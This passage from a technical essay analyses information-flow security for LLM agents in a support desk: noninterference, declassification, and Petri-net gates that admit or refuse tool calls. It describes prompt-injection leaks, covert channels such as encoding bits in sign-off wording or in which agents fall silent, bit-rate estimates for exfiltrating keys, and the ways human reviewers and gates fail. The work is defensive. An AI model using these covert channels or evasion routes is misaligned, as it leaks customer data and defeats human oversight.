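| Agent | Receives customer data | Can send outside | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Records agent | yes | no | any behaviour is safe if the rest satisfies BNDC |
| Web agent | yes, in queries | yes, by `fetch` | fails |
| Mail agent | yes, in drafts | yes, by `mail` | fails |

The web agent fails because of the query channel. If the company removes that channel, the web agent has to choose pages without knowing anything about customers, for instance by working through the manufacturers' support pages. The records agent then has to use the pages the web agent has chosen and can no longer ask about a particular fault.

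The findings still have to reach the records agent, and a direct handshake would leak:

```
Web = fetch!.findings!.Web
```

Here a records agent that refuses the findings stops the web agent after one request, which the website's owner can notice. A small trusted mailbox between the two agents avoids this:

```
Empty = put?.Full
Full  = put?.Full + take!.Empty
```

The web agent uses `put` to leave its findings in the mailbox, replacing any still there, and the records agent uses `take` to collect them. We count `put` as low and `take` as high. The only high step, `take`, leads from `Full` to `Empty`, and both states accept `put` at any time, so the mailbox satisfies persistent BNDC. The web agent, whose only actions are now `fetch` and `put`, can be any process, and so can the records agent. Even if the records agent follows hostile instructions from a web page, it cannot influence the next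 request.

Rewiring cannot do the same for the mail agent, because its job is to send customer data out. The company has to replace it with ordinary code that sends exactly the approved text. That code still fails BNDC, as `Desk` did, because BNDC rules out even permitted releases such as an approved reply.

### One process that can do anything

One can model an unknown agent as a single process that may perform or refuse any permitted action at any moment. CSP has a standard process of this kind, `CHAOS`. Toby Murray's thesis, *Analysing the Security Properties*, models untrusted software objects in a similar way and uses the model checker FDR to establish, for example, that no message carries high data to a low object.

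This works for rules about single runs. Every run of every agent is also a run of the all-purpose process, so if that process cannot break the rule, no agent can. Protocol tools can rely on the same reasoning when they check whether an attacker ever obtains a key. It does not work for noninterference, which a system can lose when some of its possible behaviours are removed. Three small processes show what goes wrong:

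```
Coin = τ.send0 + τ.send1
Any  = read0.Coin + read1.Coin + Coin
Tell = read0.send0 + read1.send1 + send0
```

`Any` may send either bit after reading a 0, after reading a 1, or without reading anything. An outsider who sees the bit learns nothing about what `Any` read, and `Any` satisfies BNDC. `Tell` sends the bit it has read, or a 0 if it has read nothing. Every trace of `Tell` is also a trace of `Any`, but `Tell` fails even SNNI, because an outsider who sees a 1 knows that the agent has read a 1. An auditor who modelled the agent as `Any` would approve the deployment even if the real agent behaved like `Tell`.

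A process refines another if all its behaviours are also behaviours of the other. Refining a secure process can make it insecure, which is known as the refinement paradox. In an example from Morgan (2006), a program sets a visible variable to an arbitrary value, which reveals nothing about a hidden variable. A programmer may refine it into a program that copies the hidden variable into the visible one, since that is one of the values allowed, and this reveals the hidden value.

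Lowe's version is closer to the case of an unknown agent. His system chooses internally between `CHAOS` and `LEAK`, a process that sends every secret it receives to the outside. `CHAOS` can already do everything `LEAK` can, so CSP's usual comparison treats the system as equal to `CHAOS`, and a definition based on that comparison accepts the system.

Pooling the behaviours of many different agents can hide a leak. Noninterference compares runs with each other, and the harmless run that makes a leaking run look secure may belong to a different agent. BNDC avoids this problem for the high processes it attaches because it tests each one separately. The problem arises when the unknown agent has low actions and we model it as a single loosely specified process.

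### Remedies for the refinement paradox

Lowe proposed calling a system secure only if all its refinements are secure. Roscoe's requirement that the low view be deterministic also avoids the paradox. But both remedies reject too many systems of several agents.

Murray shows this with a data diode, a component meant to let a low object write data and a high object read it, but let nothing pass the other way. The two objects may behave in any way. In one refinement of the whole system, the low object calls itself only if the high object has called itself first, although no message has passed between them. No diode could prevent this, so every design would fail. But two programs running separately could not behave like this unless they had some channel outside the model.

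Murray therefore refines each component separately into a program whose next step depends only on the messages it has exchanged. A system passes if it is secure for every combination of such programs. He also derived a test for this property that FDR can run automatically, using two copies of the system side by side.

A language model that samples its words can respond differently to the same messages, but it fits this scheme if we treat all its random numbers as drawn in advance. Each list of numbers then makes the agent a deterministic program. If the secret makes no difference under any list, it also makes none when the list is chosen at random, provided that the numbers do not depend on the secret.

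Murray applied the test to a published design for a diode and found a leak. Reading from that diode takes two steps, a call and a reply, and the diode accepts no writes between them. The high object can therefore block a write by calling. Murray adds that in some systems the low object would not notice, because a blocked sender just waits. In the support deployment, however, the website's owner would notice if the web agent were blocked. If the mailbox handled `take` as a request followed by a reply, the records agent could make the request and never collect the reply. The web agent would then wait to deliver its findings, and its requests to the website would stop.

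In *Refinement Operators and Information Flow Security*, Bossi, Focardi and colleagues keep the definition of security unchanged and restrict which refinements are permitted. Their example is a memory cell that holds one secret bit, which low users may overwrite but not read. Suppose a developer changes the cell so that low users can only reset it to 0, and only when it holds a 1. Every remaining step was possible before, but a low user whose reset succeeds now knows that the cell held a 1. Permitting the reset in both states removes the leak. In general, a refinement must change what low users can do in the same way in all states that look the same to them.

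This is good advice for whoever writes the mailbox, but nobody can impose it on a language model, because nobody controls how the model resolves each choice. The same limit applies to Morgan's remedy, a stricter notion of refinement that preserves the observer's ignorance. Research on the paradox continues with *Security Engineering in IIIf, Part II* (Kammüller, 2024), which addresses the refinement of noninterference in a framework for modelling insider threats, built on the proof assistant Isabelle.

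Even if each agent's behaviour were fixed, the order in which the agents run might not be. In *Information Flow in Systems with Schedulers (Part II)*, van der Meyden and Zhang (2013) study systems in which a scheduler decides who acts next. A system that is secure under a flexible scheduler can become insecure when an engineer replaces it with a more specific one. Among their definitions of security based on what an outsider can deduce, the ones that still hold after this change are those that require security even against an observer who knows the schedule. They also show that a system is secure under all schedulers exactly when it is secure under one particular scheduler, so it is enough to check that one.

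These results generally assume that scheduling does not depend on which actions the high agent chooses. Software that starts the web agent whenever the records agent finishes a case violates that assumption, and its scheduler leaks information.

### When the probabilities reveal the secret

As `Guess` showed, BNDC ignores how often an agent makes each choice. Suppose an agent that has read a secret bit reports it with probability 0.9, and otherwise tosses a fair coin to decide what to send. If it has read nothing, it just tosses the coin. Its possible steps are those of `Any`, so it satisfies BNDC. But the bit it sends after a read is correct with probability 0.9 + 0.05 = 0.95. An outsider who knows that a read took place, and who previously thought both values equally likely, is now 95% sure. In the usual measure of information, the outsider has learned

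```
1 + 0.95 × log2(0.95) + 0.05 × log2(0.05)  ≈  0.71 bits
```

out of one. Repetition removes most of the remaining doubt. A ten-digit phone number fits into 34 bits. If the agent sends each bit five times with fresh coin tosses, and the outsider takes the majority each time, 170 messages are enough to recover the whole number correctly in about 96% of cases.

Probabilistic noninterference closes this gap by comparing probabilities as well as possible steps. *Noninterference Analysis of Irreversible Systems and Reversible Systems* (Esposito, Aldini and Bernardo, 2025) uses a model with two kinds of state. In the first, several actions are possible and have no probabilities attached, while in the second, the process moves to its next state at random, with known probabilities. This mixture suits agents better than an earlier approach that also attached probabilities to parallel composition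 and hiding, because an attacker's choices and the order of events have no known probabilities.

They then adapt weak bisimilarity to this model. Equivalent states must move into each group of equivalent states with the same total probability. When one process performs an action, the other must have some way of making its open choices that performs the same action, internal steps being ignored, and is certain to arrive at an equivalent state. Noninterference compares the system with its high actions forbidden and with them hidden, as before, but under this stricter equivalence. For the leaking agent, the relevant probabilities are:

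| Before sending, the agent | sends 0 | sends 1 |
|---|---|---|
| read a 0 | 0.95 | 0.05 |
| read a 1 | 0.05 | 0.95 |
| read nothing | 0.5 | 0.5 |

The agent can reach only the last row when the high actions are forbidden, but it can reach all three when they are hidden. Nothing in the restricted system matches the first two rows, so the agent fails the check. It would pass if all three rows were the same.

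Exact equality is a strict requirement, since even a difference of one in a million counts as a failure. Bossi and colleagues mention an approach by Di Pierro, Hankin and Wiklicky that ignores differences below a chosen threshold. The threshold has to reflect how many messages the outsider can collect, because small differences add up.

Such a table is much harder to fill in for a real agent. A language model computes a probability for each possible next piece of text, so whoever runs it can work out how likely one exact message is. But the table needs the total probability of all messages that convey the bit, in any wording or code the agent and the outsider might share. It also needs a separate set of rows for every web page an attacker might write.

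Testing gives only rough limits. If 1,000 test runs produce no leak, we can be 95% confident that the leak rate on similar inputs is below about 0.3%. For a company with 10,000 cases a day, that allows up to about 30 leaks a day. The limit also doesn't cover inputs unlike those tested, which an attacker will look for. Testing cannot show that two probabilities are exactly equal, however many runs are made.

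A new version of the model, a change to its instructions or a different sampling setting can also alter all the figures, and the company would then have to measure them again. The arrangement with the mailbox does not need these figures. The web agent there also chooses its requests at random, but nothing the records agent does can change the probabilities.

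## Permitted release of secret data

Noninterference rejects the support deployment's approved replies and other useful programs. *Declassification*, by Sabelfeld and Sands, mentions one program that publishes the average of some secret salaries and another that checks passwords. The password check reveals a little even when it refuses a login, because the caller learns that one password is wrong. The company needs a definition that permits such releases, known as declassification or downgrading, without permitting every other leak.

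The simplest remedy is to exempt the mail code from the rules. Designers of multilevel systems did this with "trusted subjects", programs that could break the rules on reading and writing. The drawback, according to *Security Requirements Specifications* (Rushby, 2001), was that no overall specification limited what these programs could do.

### Release through one designated step

Intransitive noninterference allows secret data to be released only through a designated step. Normally, if information may flow from A to B and from B to C, it may also flow from A to C. An intransitive policy allows the first two flows but forbids a direct flow from A to C. For example, customer data may pass from the high part to a releasing step and from there to the low part, but never directly from high to low. Rushby calls such policies "surprisingly difficult to specify correctly" and cites a series of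 papers that each found flaws in the one before.

For Petri nets, Best and colleagues divide the transitions into high, releasing and low. The secret is whether any high transition has fired since the last release. Each release cancels the old secret and starts a new one. A net satisfies their bisimulation-based property, BINI, if it satisfies BNDC with its releasing transitions deleted, both from the starting marking and from every marking that a release can lead to. They prove that this is the same as a condition on single steps:

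```
for every reachable marking M and every high step from M to M′:
    N \ (High ∪ Release) has the same low sequences from M and from M′
```

The property is decidable even if places can hold any number of tokens. The test is almost the same as the two-copy test that decides plain BNDC.

An approved reply, without the web agent, looks like this as a net:

```
lookup  (high):       case    →  record
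draft   (high):       record  →  draft
approve (releasing):  draft   →  outbox
mail    (low):        outbox  →  case
```

Deleting the high and releasing transitions leaves only `mail`, which needs a mark in `outbox`. Neither `lookup` nor `draft` adds or removes marks there, so no high step changes whether `mail` can fire, and the net passes. If `draft` put its mark directly into `outbox`, a high step would allow `mail` to fire and the net would fail.

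Bossi, Piazza and Rossi, in *Modelling Downgrading in Information Flow Security*, give a matching condition for the Security Process Algebra, which they extend with releasing actions. It is persistent BNDC with the releasing actions forbidden along with the high ones:

```
for every reachable state F and every high step from F to G,
    F can reach some G′ by zero or more τ steps such that
    G \ (High ∪ Release)  and  G′ \ (High ∪ Release)  are weakly bisimilar
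```

`Desk`, the nine-state system of records agent and mail agent, failed plain noninterference but passes this test once we count `approve` as a releasing action. Six of its states allow a high step, which is always a lookup or the arrival of a record. The high step never changes how many mails can go out, which is exactly one if the mail agent has an approved draft at that moment and none otherwise.

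Adding the web agent makes the system fail, because the high step `record?(x)` then makes the request `fetch!(x)` possible without an approval. The phone number took this route.

### Leaks around the release

Checking a system only from its starting state can miss leaks. Bossi and colleagues describe a program that receives a secret file, encrypts it (the releasing action), waits for a confidential acknowledgement and then sends the encrypted file. The program satisfies BNDC because, from its starting state, it can do nothing when high and releasing actions are forbidden, whichever high process we attach. But after encryption, the high user can delay the file by withholding the acknowledgement. The condition above detects this leak because it covers every reachable state. The leak disappears if the program sends the file anyway after a timeout.

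The support deployment would have the same fault if the mail agent waited for the records agent to log each approved reply before sending it. A hijacked records agent could then signal by delaying the log entry.

Joining processes can also break the condition. If one process waits for an approval and another supplies it, each can pass alone while the pair fails, because synchronising turns the approval into an ordinary τ, which the check no longer counts as a release. We avoided this in `Desk` by leaving the person outside the model. Systems that never synchronise with each other on releasing actions can safely run in parallel. Checking a system of `n` states takes time at most proportional to `n` cubed.

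Both definitions ignore signals sent by preventing a visible event. In an example from Best and colleagues, a guard opens and closes a shop, and while it is closed a friend borrows an article and brings it back. Customers notice nothing. But the friend could keep the guard from ever reopening the shop, which customers would notice, and BINI still accepts the system. Similarly, a records agent could signal a bit by drafting a reply to only one of two waiting customers, even though every mail sent had its approval.

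### Where is not what

A more serious objection is that a release clears everything that came before it. Suppose the mail agent holds the customer's record `x` and a stranger's record `y`:

```
Bundle = record?(x).record?(y).approve?.mail!(x,y)
```

`Bundle` satisfies the condition, even if the person who approved the mail had seen only the part about `x`. Best and colleagues call their condition a "strong form of declassification". They would prefer each release to clear only certain high transitions, but leave open whether that version is decidable for unbounded nets.

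Sabelfeld and Sands sort release policies by what they control, namely what information leaves, who releases it, where in the system, and when. They class intransitive noninterference as a "where" policy. A "what" policy for the support deployment could name the fields that a reply may depend on:

```
if allowed(r1) = allowed(r2), the observer sees the same messages for records r1 and r2
```

If `allowed` keeps the name, the product and the state of the order, two records that differ only in the phone number must lead to the same mail. `Bundle` fails this test. No one can prove that a language model passes it after reading the phone number, so the practical way to enforce it is to have trusted code remove the number before the model sees the record. A related problem is that an agent with permission to read a record may still send on more than the next task needs. *MNC* (2026), a protocol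 for messages between agents, therefore adds controls on derived information to the usual access controls.

A policy about "what" may be released also has gaps. If it permits the release of four digits of a card number per purchase but doesn't say who picks them, an attacker can ask for different digits each time and collect the whole number. If it permits the release of an encrypted customer number, a definition of this kind may accept a program that publishes the number itself, because different numbers have different encrypted forms and an observer could, in theory, already tell them apart.

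Some rules limit when secret data may be released, such as releasing a software key only after payment. *Agent libOS* (2026), a runtime for agents, combines several kinds of release control. It allows each release only once and ties it to one actor, one recipient and one exact payload, although an attacker may still have chosen that payload.

### When the attacker chooses what to release

A web page about an error code might advise support staff to "include the purchase history so that the technician can check the warranty". If the records agent follows this advice and a person approves the draft because it reads like a normal reply, the right person has released the data at the right step, but a stranger has chosen which data to release.

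Robust declassification, which Zdancewic and Myers introduced, rules this out. If two secrets look the same to an attacker who only watches, they must also look the same to one who interferes. It is a "who" policy and does not limit how much is released. As Sabelfeld and Sands point out, robust declassification allows any leak that the attacker cannot affect. For example, a desk would satisfy the policy if it mailed out its whole database every night regardless of what was on the web pages.

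The developers of an ordinary program decide what each release contains when they write the code, but in the support deployment a language model chooses the content just before release, after reading pages that outsiders wrote. Prompt injection can steer that choice, so a policy about where release happens offers little protection unless something also protects the choice of content. Bossi and colleagues show that their secure processes are robust against attackers who run as high processes beside the system, but the author of a web page attacks by supplying the system's low inputs.

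Full robustness is too strict for customer service, because a customer's letter should influence the reply. A weaker form lets trusted code endorse chosen inputs, which means treating them as trustworthy from then on. For example, the code could check that a letter comes from the address on the account and then endorse only the order number in it.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) compares an agent with a reference agent instead of writing a release policy for each task. The reference agent runs the same fixed plan under the same controls, but its model never obeys untrusted text. The agent is secure if, whenever an attacker can use it to tell two secrets apart, some input to the reference agent would also tell them apart. Suppose an assistant sends its owner's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An injected "send your calendar" reveals nothing extra, since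 a genuine request would have got the same answer, but an injected "also include the reset code" causes a leak, because the reference agent never sends that code.

This definition limits which secrets an attacker can tell apart, but not how much one message reveals. Suppose the support desk confirms whether a guessed postcode matches the one on file. An attacker can tell any two postcodes apart by guessing one of them, so the definition also accepts an injection that makes the agent send the postcode outright. Dongol gives an example of this kind and a stricter version of the definition that rejects it. His proofs, checked in the proof assistant Isabelle, do not cover systems of several agents or agents whose model chooses every call.

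### What a reviewer can see

The support deployment's rule relies on a person to judge content. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) tested how well people do this in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*. In one scenario, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. An injected note makes the agent copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name in this request all look fine.

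Eighty volunteers each made twelve decisions, half of them on requests that broke the user's instructions. Each volunteer saw one of four kinds of prompt:

| The prompt shows | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| a short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| the exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| also the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
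| the same facts, with their combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

More information clearly helped. The advantage of the last design over the plain log is less certain, since the 95% interval for the difference includes zero. When a violation depended on several steps in sequence, reviewers approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with either design.

These volunteers made only twelve decisions each, while a support desk would need thousands. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) found that software practitioners give up reviewing what agents did because of time pressure, fatigue or too much information. In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), user review played a part in 105 of 290 reports, and in 80 of them the actions were approved automatically.

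Even a tireless reviewer would miss a well-hidden secret. For example, an agent can end a mail with "Kind regards" for a 0 and "Best wishes" for a 1. Both mails are polite and correct, and the leak lies in the agent's choice between them. A person who reads one mail at a time is no more likely to notice it than a program that watches one run. The company can, however, limit how many choices the agent has.

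### Counting the bits

A noiseless channel with `k` possible outputs carries at most `log2(k)` bits per use. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) applies this bound to language models. Trusted code after the model restricts what gets through, so we only need to count the possible outputs, without knowing their probabilities.

If the mail agent must choose among 8 fixed templates, such as "restart the router" or "install the new firmware", each message carries at most `log2(8) = 3` bits. A hijacked agent would then need at least 43 messages to send out a 128-bit encryption key. If it could write unrestricted text, a single 1,000-byte message could carry 8,000 bits, enough for 62 such keys.

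Between these extremes, the result depends on who makes each choice:

| Outgoing mail | Bits per message | Messages for a 128-bit key |
|---|---|---|
| 1,000 bytes of any content | 8,000 | 1 |
| Natural text with 20 free choices between two wordings | 20 | 7 |
| 8 templates, and the agent picks one of 30 dates | 7.9 | 17 |
| 8 templates | 3 | 43 |
| 8 templates, of which a reviewer accepts only two | 1 | 128 |

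The second row is a guess at the capacity that might remain after a reviewer rejects everything that looks odd. Even if reviewing free text cuts the capacity enormously, a key can still leak within a morning. In the third row, the agent fills in a blank. If trusted code copies the delivery date from the order instead, the agent cannot influence it and the figure falls back to 3 bits. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026) proposes releases of this kind, in which a model may suggest a value but trusted code checks it and issues it in a narrow format, such as a time interval or an item from a short list, and never as free text.

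These figures are upper limits that include legitimate content. If the fault requires new firmware, the customer is supposed to learn that from the choice of template. The figures also cover only the choice of template. An agent that controls the order in which ten replies go out to different customers can choose among 3,628,800 orders, which can carry almost 22 more bits, so trusted code should set the order too. If the agent can choose to send nothing, that option counts as a ninth template.

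A rate limit slows the leak but doesn't reduce the bits per message. At one reply a day, leaking the key takes 43 days. A desk that answers 10,000 cases a day can't work at that pace. At 3 bits each, its replies could carry 30,000 bits a day, enough for some 880 phone numbers. A limit for each recipient would slow an attacker who sees only mail to their own account, but we have assumed an observer who sees all the mail.

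*L3M* (2026) caps the total leak at the amount of private data the agent has read, since an agent cannot leak more about a secret than it has taken in. An agent that has read 64 bytes of private data and sends two 50-byte requests has leaked at most 64 bytes, not 100. The system counts each outgoing request at its full length, since any byte could carry secret data. If the records agent starts afresh for each case and receives only that customer's record, it has no key and no other customer's number to send, but it also can't use what its predecessor learned from a similar fault. The cap fails if any data reaches the agent without being counted.

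The other limits have greater drawbacks. With only eight templates, the agent cannot explain an unusual fault, so staff have to handle those cases. If the best results of Hossain and colleagues carried over to 10,000 replies a day, reviewing a day's replies would take about 92 hours of work, or twelve people, who would also reject about 1,400 good replies. The company could reduce the agent's share to zero bits by having a person read the letter and choose the template without seeing the agent's suggestion. If staff see the suggestion and usually accept it, the agent regains most of its 3 bits.

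## Gates that admit or refuse each action

Templates, rate limits and approvals only help if the agents cannot bypass them. Because an agent only proposes its actions, the company can put trusted software, called a gate, between the agents and their tools to admit or refuse each action. The gate can record everything the agents have done so far in a run, but it cannot observe what they might have done instead, which noninterference depends on.

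### What a gate can enforce

Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies*, worked out in 2000 which rules a program can enforce by watching another program's steps and stopping it just before a violation. Such a rule must meet three conditions:

- Each run passes or fails on its own, whatever other runs the system has.
- Once a run has broken the rule, nothing that happens later can repair it.
- A run that breaks the rule does so after finitely many steps.

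Rules like this are called safety properties. In one of Schneider's examples, a program may not send messages after it has read a file. An automaton with two states can enforce this. It starts in a state that allows everything, and the first read moves it to a state that allows everything except sending. "Every letter eventually gets an answer" is not a safety property, because an answer may still come however long the customer has waited.

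A gate cannot enforce every safety property. "Every letter gets an answer within an hour" meets all three conditions, but no gate can prevent time from passing. Basin et al. (2012) therefore refined Schneider's result by separating the actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) adapts the theory to gates for AI agents. The gate must never let a run break the rule or interfere with a run that obeys it. Ray proves that such a gate can enforce exactly those safety properties whose permitted runs it can recognise with the memory it has. Software that can hold actions back can enforce more, such as a rule that a confirmation must follow every payment, by delaying each payment until the confirmation arrives. A gate cannot enforce this rule because it has to decide immediately. If it admits the payment, the confirmation may never come, and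 if it refuses, it may block a run that would have obeyed the rule.

This result assumes that the gate correctly evaluates the conditions in its rule. The rule "Never mail personal data to an unapproved recipient" depends on a classifier that recognises personal data, and classifiers make mistakes. Rules are safer when they rely on facts that trusted software records directly, such as whether an agent has opened a customer record.

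Noninterference fails the first of Schneider's conditions. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) calls a rule about single runs a trace property and a rule about the whole set of a system's runs a hyperproperty. Goguen and Meseguer's noninterference is a hyperproperty because it allows a run only if the system also has one with the same low events and no high inputs. A gate observes only the current run, so it cannot check whether the other exists. The paper also shows that BNDC is a hyperproperty, provided that runs record enough about each state. Some hyperproperties require only that any two runs that start out looking the same to a low observer continue to look the same. Two recorded runs can prove a violation of such a rule, but only after the messages have been sent. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025) surveys the logics since developed for hyperproperties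 and the algorithms for checking and monitoring them.

The usual way round the problem, which Schneider mentions in a footnote, is to enforce a stricter rule about single runs.

### No sending after reading

Schneider's rule about files is of this kind. Suppose that reading records is an agent's only high action and sending outside is its only low one. In a run that obeys the rule, every send comes before every read, so deleting the reads leaves the beginning of the run, which is itself a possible run. Deleting the high actions therefore always leaves a possible run, which is the condition for SNNI. The argument does not depend on how the agent behaves, so it still holds if an update removes some of the agent's behaviours.

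The gate also refuses some harmless actions. `Either`, which can send with or without a read, was secure, but the gate would stop it from sending after a read.

With several agents, the gate also has to follow the messages between them, or the records agent could read and the web agent could send. A small Petri net can do this. Each agent `i` has a place `clean_i` and a place `exposed_i`, with one mark between them that starts in `clean_i`:

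```
read_i   (high):   clean_i               →  exposed_i
tell_ij  (high):   exposed_i + clean_j   →  exposed_i + exposed_j
send_i   (low):    clean_i               →  clean_i
```

An agent's first read moves its mark. A message from an exposed agent exposes the agent that receives it. Sending requires a mark in `clean_i` and puts it back. The list leaves out steps that change no marks, such as messages between clean agents or further reads by an exposed agent.

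This stops the theft of the phone number through the web address:

| Step | Records agent | Web agent |
|---|---|---|
| The web agent fetches a page about the error code | clean | clean |
| The records agent looks up the customer | exposed | clean |
| The records agent sends a query with the phone number | exposed | exposed |
| The web agent proposes a request with the number in the address | gate refuses | gate refuses |

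The gate never examines the address, so it makes no difference how the attacker disguises the number. However, at this point it would also refuse a request with a plain error code. The agents must search before anyone opens a record, and the company needs new agents with empty memories for the next case.

The argument about deleted reads extends to this net if agents leave messages in mailboxes that never refuse them. If we delete from any run everything each agent did from the moment of its exposure, the remaining steps, which include every send, belong to clean agents. These agents had received nothing from exposed ones, so they could have taken the same steps without any reads. The deployment therefore satisfies NDC, whichever models run the agents, as long as the agents have no other way to influence each other.

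It does not satisfy BNDC, because `clean_i` is a conflict place: both a high and a low transition take its mark. An agent can send any number of times before its first read, but cannot send afterwards. An outsider may notice that the requests have stopped. Traces do not show this, because an agent that never reads anything may also stop sending.

A hijacked records agent can leak data by making chosen web agents stop. Suppose the company runs 34 web agents, each working through a different manufacturer's site. The records agent reads a phone number, writes it as 34 bits, and sends a message to each web agent whose bit is 1. Those agents become exposed and stop sending requests. The observer can work out the number from which sites still get requests, although no web agent has sent a request after becoming exposed.

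The gate can close this channel by refusing messages from exposed agents to clean ones instead of exposing the receiver. The web agents then keep working regardless of what the records agent does. Only the records agent learns of the refusal, and it is already exposed. This is the earlier arrangement, in which the web agent received no queries and left its findings in a mailbox. Exposing the receiver is more flexible because any agent may talk to any other, but it leaks information when a web agent falls silent.

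Neither version lets the mail agent answer customers, because its drafts come from an exposed agent. An approved reply needs a separate transition that requires an approval instead of a mark in `clean`.

### A harness built on a Petri net

Gu and Zhu (2026), in *Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI*, use a Petri net as the memory of a gate. Their example is an agent that writes a software patch, has it tested and scanned, gets a person's approval and releases it. An instruction hidden in the bug description might tell the agent to release the patch immediately. A rule against this in the agent's prompt would only be text, like the attacker's instruction, so the agent could fail to follow it.

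In their design, the gate executes a proposed tool call only if it passes four checks:

1. An interface can match the proposal to a transition of the net that belongs to the agent making it.
2. A validator accepts the arguments, for instance because the recipient is on a list.
3. The transition is enabled at the current marking.
4. A supervisor, which is a table computed in advance, permits the transition at this marking.

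If any check fails, the agent gets an error message and may propose something else. The first check alone prevents an agent from approving its own draft, because `approve` is reserved for a person. Schlapbach's extended protocol did not ensure this.

The third check enforces the order of the work. An approval is a mark, and the modeller decides whether an action spends it or only tests for it. If `mail` spends approvals and only `approve` produces them, then at every moment

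```
marks in approved  =  approvals given − mails sent  ≥  0
```

Each `mail` action uses up one approval mark, so the agents can never send more mails than people have approved, whatever instructions they read on a web page. If `mail` only checked that a mark was present, one approval would authorise any number of mails, as it would with a simple "approved" flag in a database.

Marks can also have colours, as in coloured nets. Gu and Zhu colour each approval with a digest, a short code computed from the approved item that in practice no other item shares. In the support deployment, the digest could cover a reply's text and recipient. If the mail agent adds another customer's record to an approved draft, the digest no longer matches and the gate refuses the mail. This prevents the leak that passed every check of message order.

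The place `approved` is an example of a monitor place, which enforces a limit on how often transitions fire. Suppose the company allows 20 web requests for each letter. A monitor place gets 20 marks when a letter arrives, and every request takes one. In general, a single place can enforce any rule of the form

```
c1 × (firings of t1)  +  c2 × (firings of t2)  +  ...  ≤  b
```

with whole numbers for `b` and the coefficients, and `b` not negative. The place starts with `b` marks. A transition with a positive coefficient takes that many marks each time it fires, and one with a negative coefficient adds them. The rule for letters has coefficients 1 for a request and −20 for a letter, with `b` equal to 0. No one has to list the net's markings for this, so the number of letters can be unlimited. However, the gate must be able to refuse every transition that takes marks from the place.

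### Events that a gate cannot refuse

A gate can refuse an agent's tool calls, but not their results, a person's decision or a customer's next letter. Gu and Zhu call events that a gate cannot refuse "uncontrollable". Because of these events, the gate may have to refuse an action that is harmless in itself but could lead to a violation that nobody can then prevent.

Suppose the mail agent puts approved replies into a mail server's queue, and the server sends them whenever it is ready. Meanwhile, the customer can withdraw permission to use their data, after which no reply may go out. The agent can discard a reply before it goes out. The gate controls `queue` and `discard`, but not `withdraw` or `deliver`.

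To compute a supervisor, we begin with all reachable markings and remove the forbidden ones, here those in which a reply went out after a withdrawal. Then we remove every marking from which an uncontrollable event leads to a marking already removed, and repeat this until nothing changes:

1. If the reply is in the queue and the customer has withdrawn, `deliver` leads to a forbidden marking, so we remove this marking.
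2. If the reply is in the queue and the customer has not withdrawn, `withdraw` leads to the marking we have just removed, so we remove this one too.

No marking with a reply in the queue remains, so the supervisor must always refuse `queue`. This is safe, but the agent can only discard its replies.

A supervisor could stay safe within the remaining markings by refusing everything, but then the task might never end. Gu and Zhu therefore also remove markings from which no run can finish the task, hand it to a person or stop properly. After this removal, an uncontrollable event can lead from a remaining marking to a removed one, so they alternate the two kinds of removal until neither changes anything. The final supervisor permits an action exactly when it leads to a remaining marking. Gu and Zhu adapt a 1980s result by Ramadge and Wonham to prove that this supervisor is the most permissive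 possible, meaning that any other supervisor that is safe and always leaves a way to finish permits only a subset of its actions. If the starting marking is removed, no such supervisor exists.

The solution is to change the mail server rather than the gate. If the server holds each reply until the agent proposes a separate `release`, the gate can check for a withdrawal at the last moment. Gu and Zhu found the same fault in their release agent, where an incident can freeze all releases after a rollout has started. When the rollout completed by itself, the net had 30 reachable markings, and no safe supervisor could allow any release. After they split the rollout into two steps, the net had 32 markings, and the supervisor could allow releases while avoiding only the two forbidden markings. Designers can therefore use the method to find the missing step before anyone runs the system.

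### From the net to the running system

A supervisor that is safe on the net might fail in practice. Gu and Zhu prove that its safety carries over to the running system under four assumptions. The fourth has two parts:

| Assumption | What can happen without it |
|---|---|
| 1. The starting marking describes the system as it really starts | The net starts with an approval that nobody gave |
| 2. Each admitted action or outside event changes the system as its transition changes the marking | The interface mistakes a call that deletes the live database for one that deletes a test copy |
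| 3. Every marking that is not forbidden describes a safe state | The modeller forgets to forbid the markings in which a password has leaked |
| 4a. Every action with consequences passes through the gate | The agent releases the software directly from a command line |
| 4b. The gate learns of every outside event | An incident freezes releases, but nobody tells the gate, which admits one |

The proof is by induction on the steps of a run. The marking matches the system at the start (first assumption). Every later step is an admitted action, a reported event or something internal, such as the model writing a plan (fourth assumption), and the marking still matches after each of these (second assumption). The supervisor keeps the net out of forbidden markings, so the system is safe (third assumption).

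Security engineers call assumption 4a complete mediation. Schneider pointed out that a program may have many ways to send a message, some of them obscure, and that a rule against sending must cover them all. Gu and Zhu suggest running the agent in a sandbox and giving the credentials for its tools only to a trusted broker, so that the agent can use the tools only through the broker. This arrangement does not cover the shared disk in the support deployment, which is a channel outside the gate.

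A sandbox cannot ensure 4b, because outside events don't start with the agent. The gate receives the results of the calls it executes, and it can require people to give approvals through its own interface. For other events, it needs an authenticated report from the source. In the mail example, the gate could query the customer database for withdrawals just before each release.

The second assumption holds only if the gate handles proposals one at a time. Otherwise two agents could use the same approval at once. Gu and Zhu consider the interface the part most prone to error, which is plausible because the interface must turn a model's free-form request into exactly one transition.

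Gu and Zhu's guarantee covers which actions occur, in what order and how often, but not leaks through the arguments of permitted calls. If the net permits a web request and the validator accepts the address, the request goes out, even if it contains a phone number. Gu and Zhu do not analyse the validator, and they also exclude the case where a person approves something malicious. Adding the clean and exposed places to their harness would prevent the leak through the web request, but only by refusing every request from an exposed agent.

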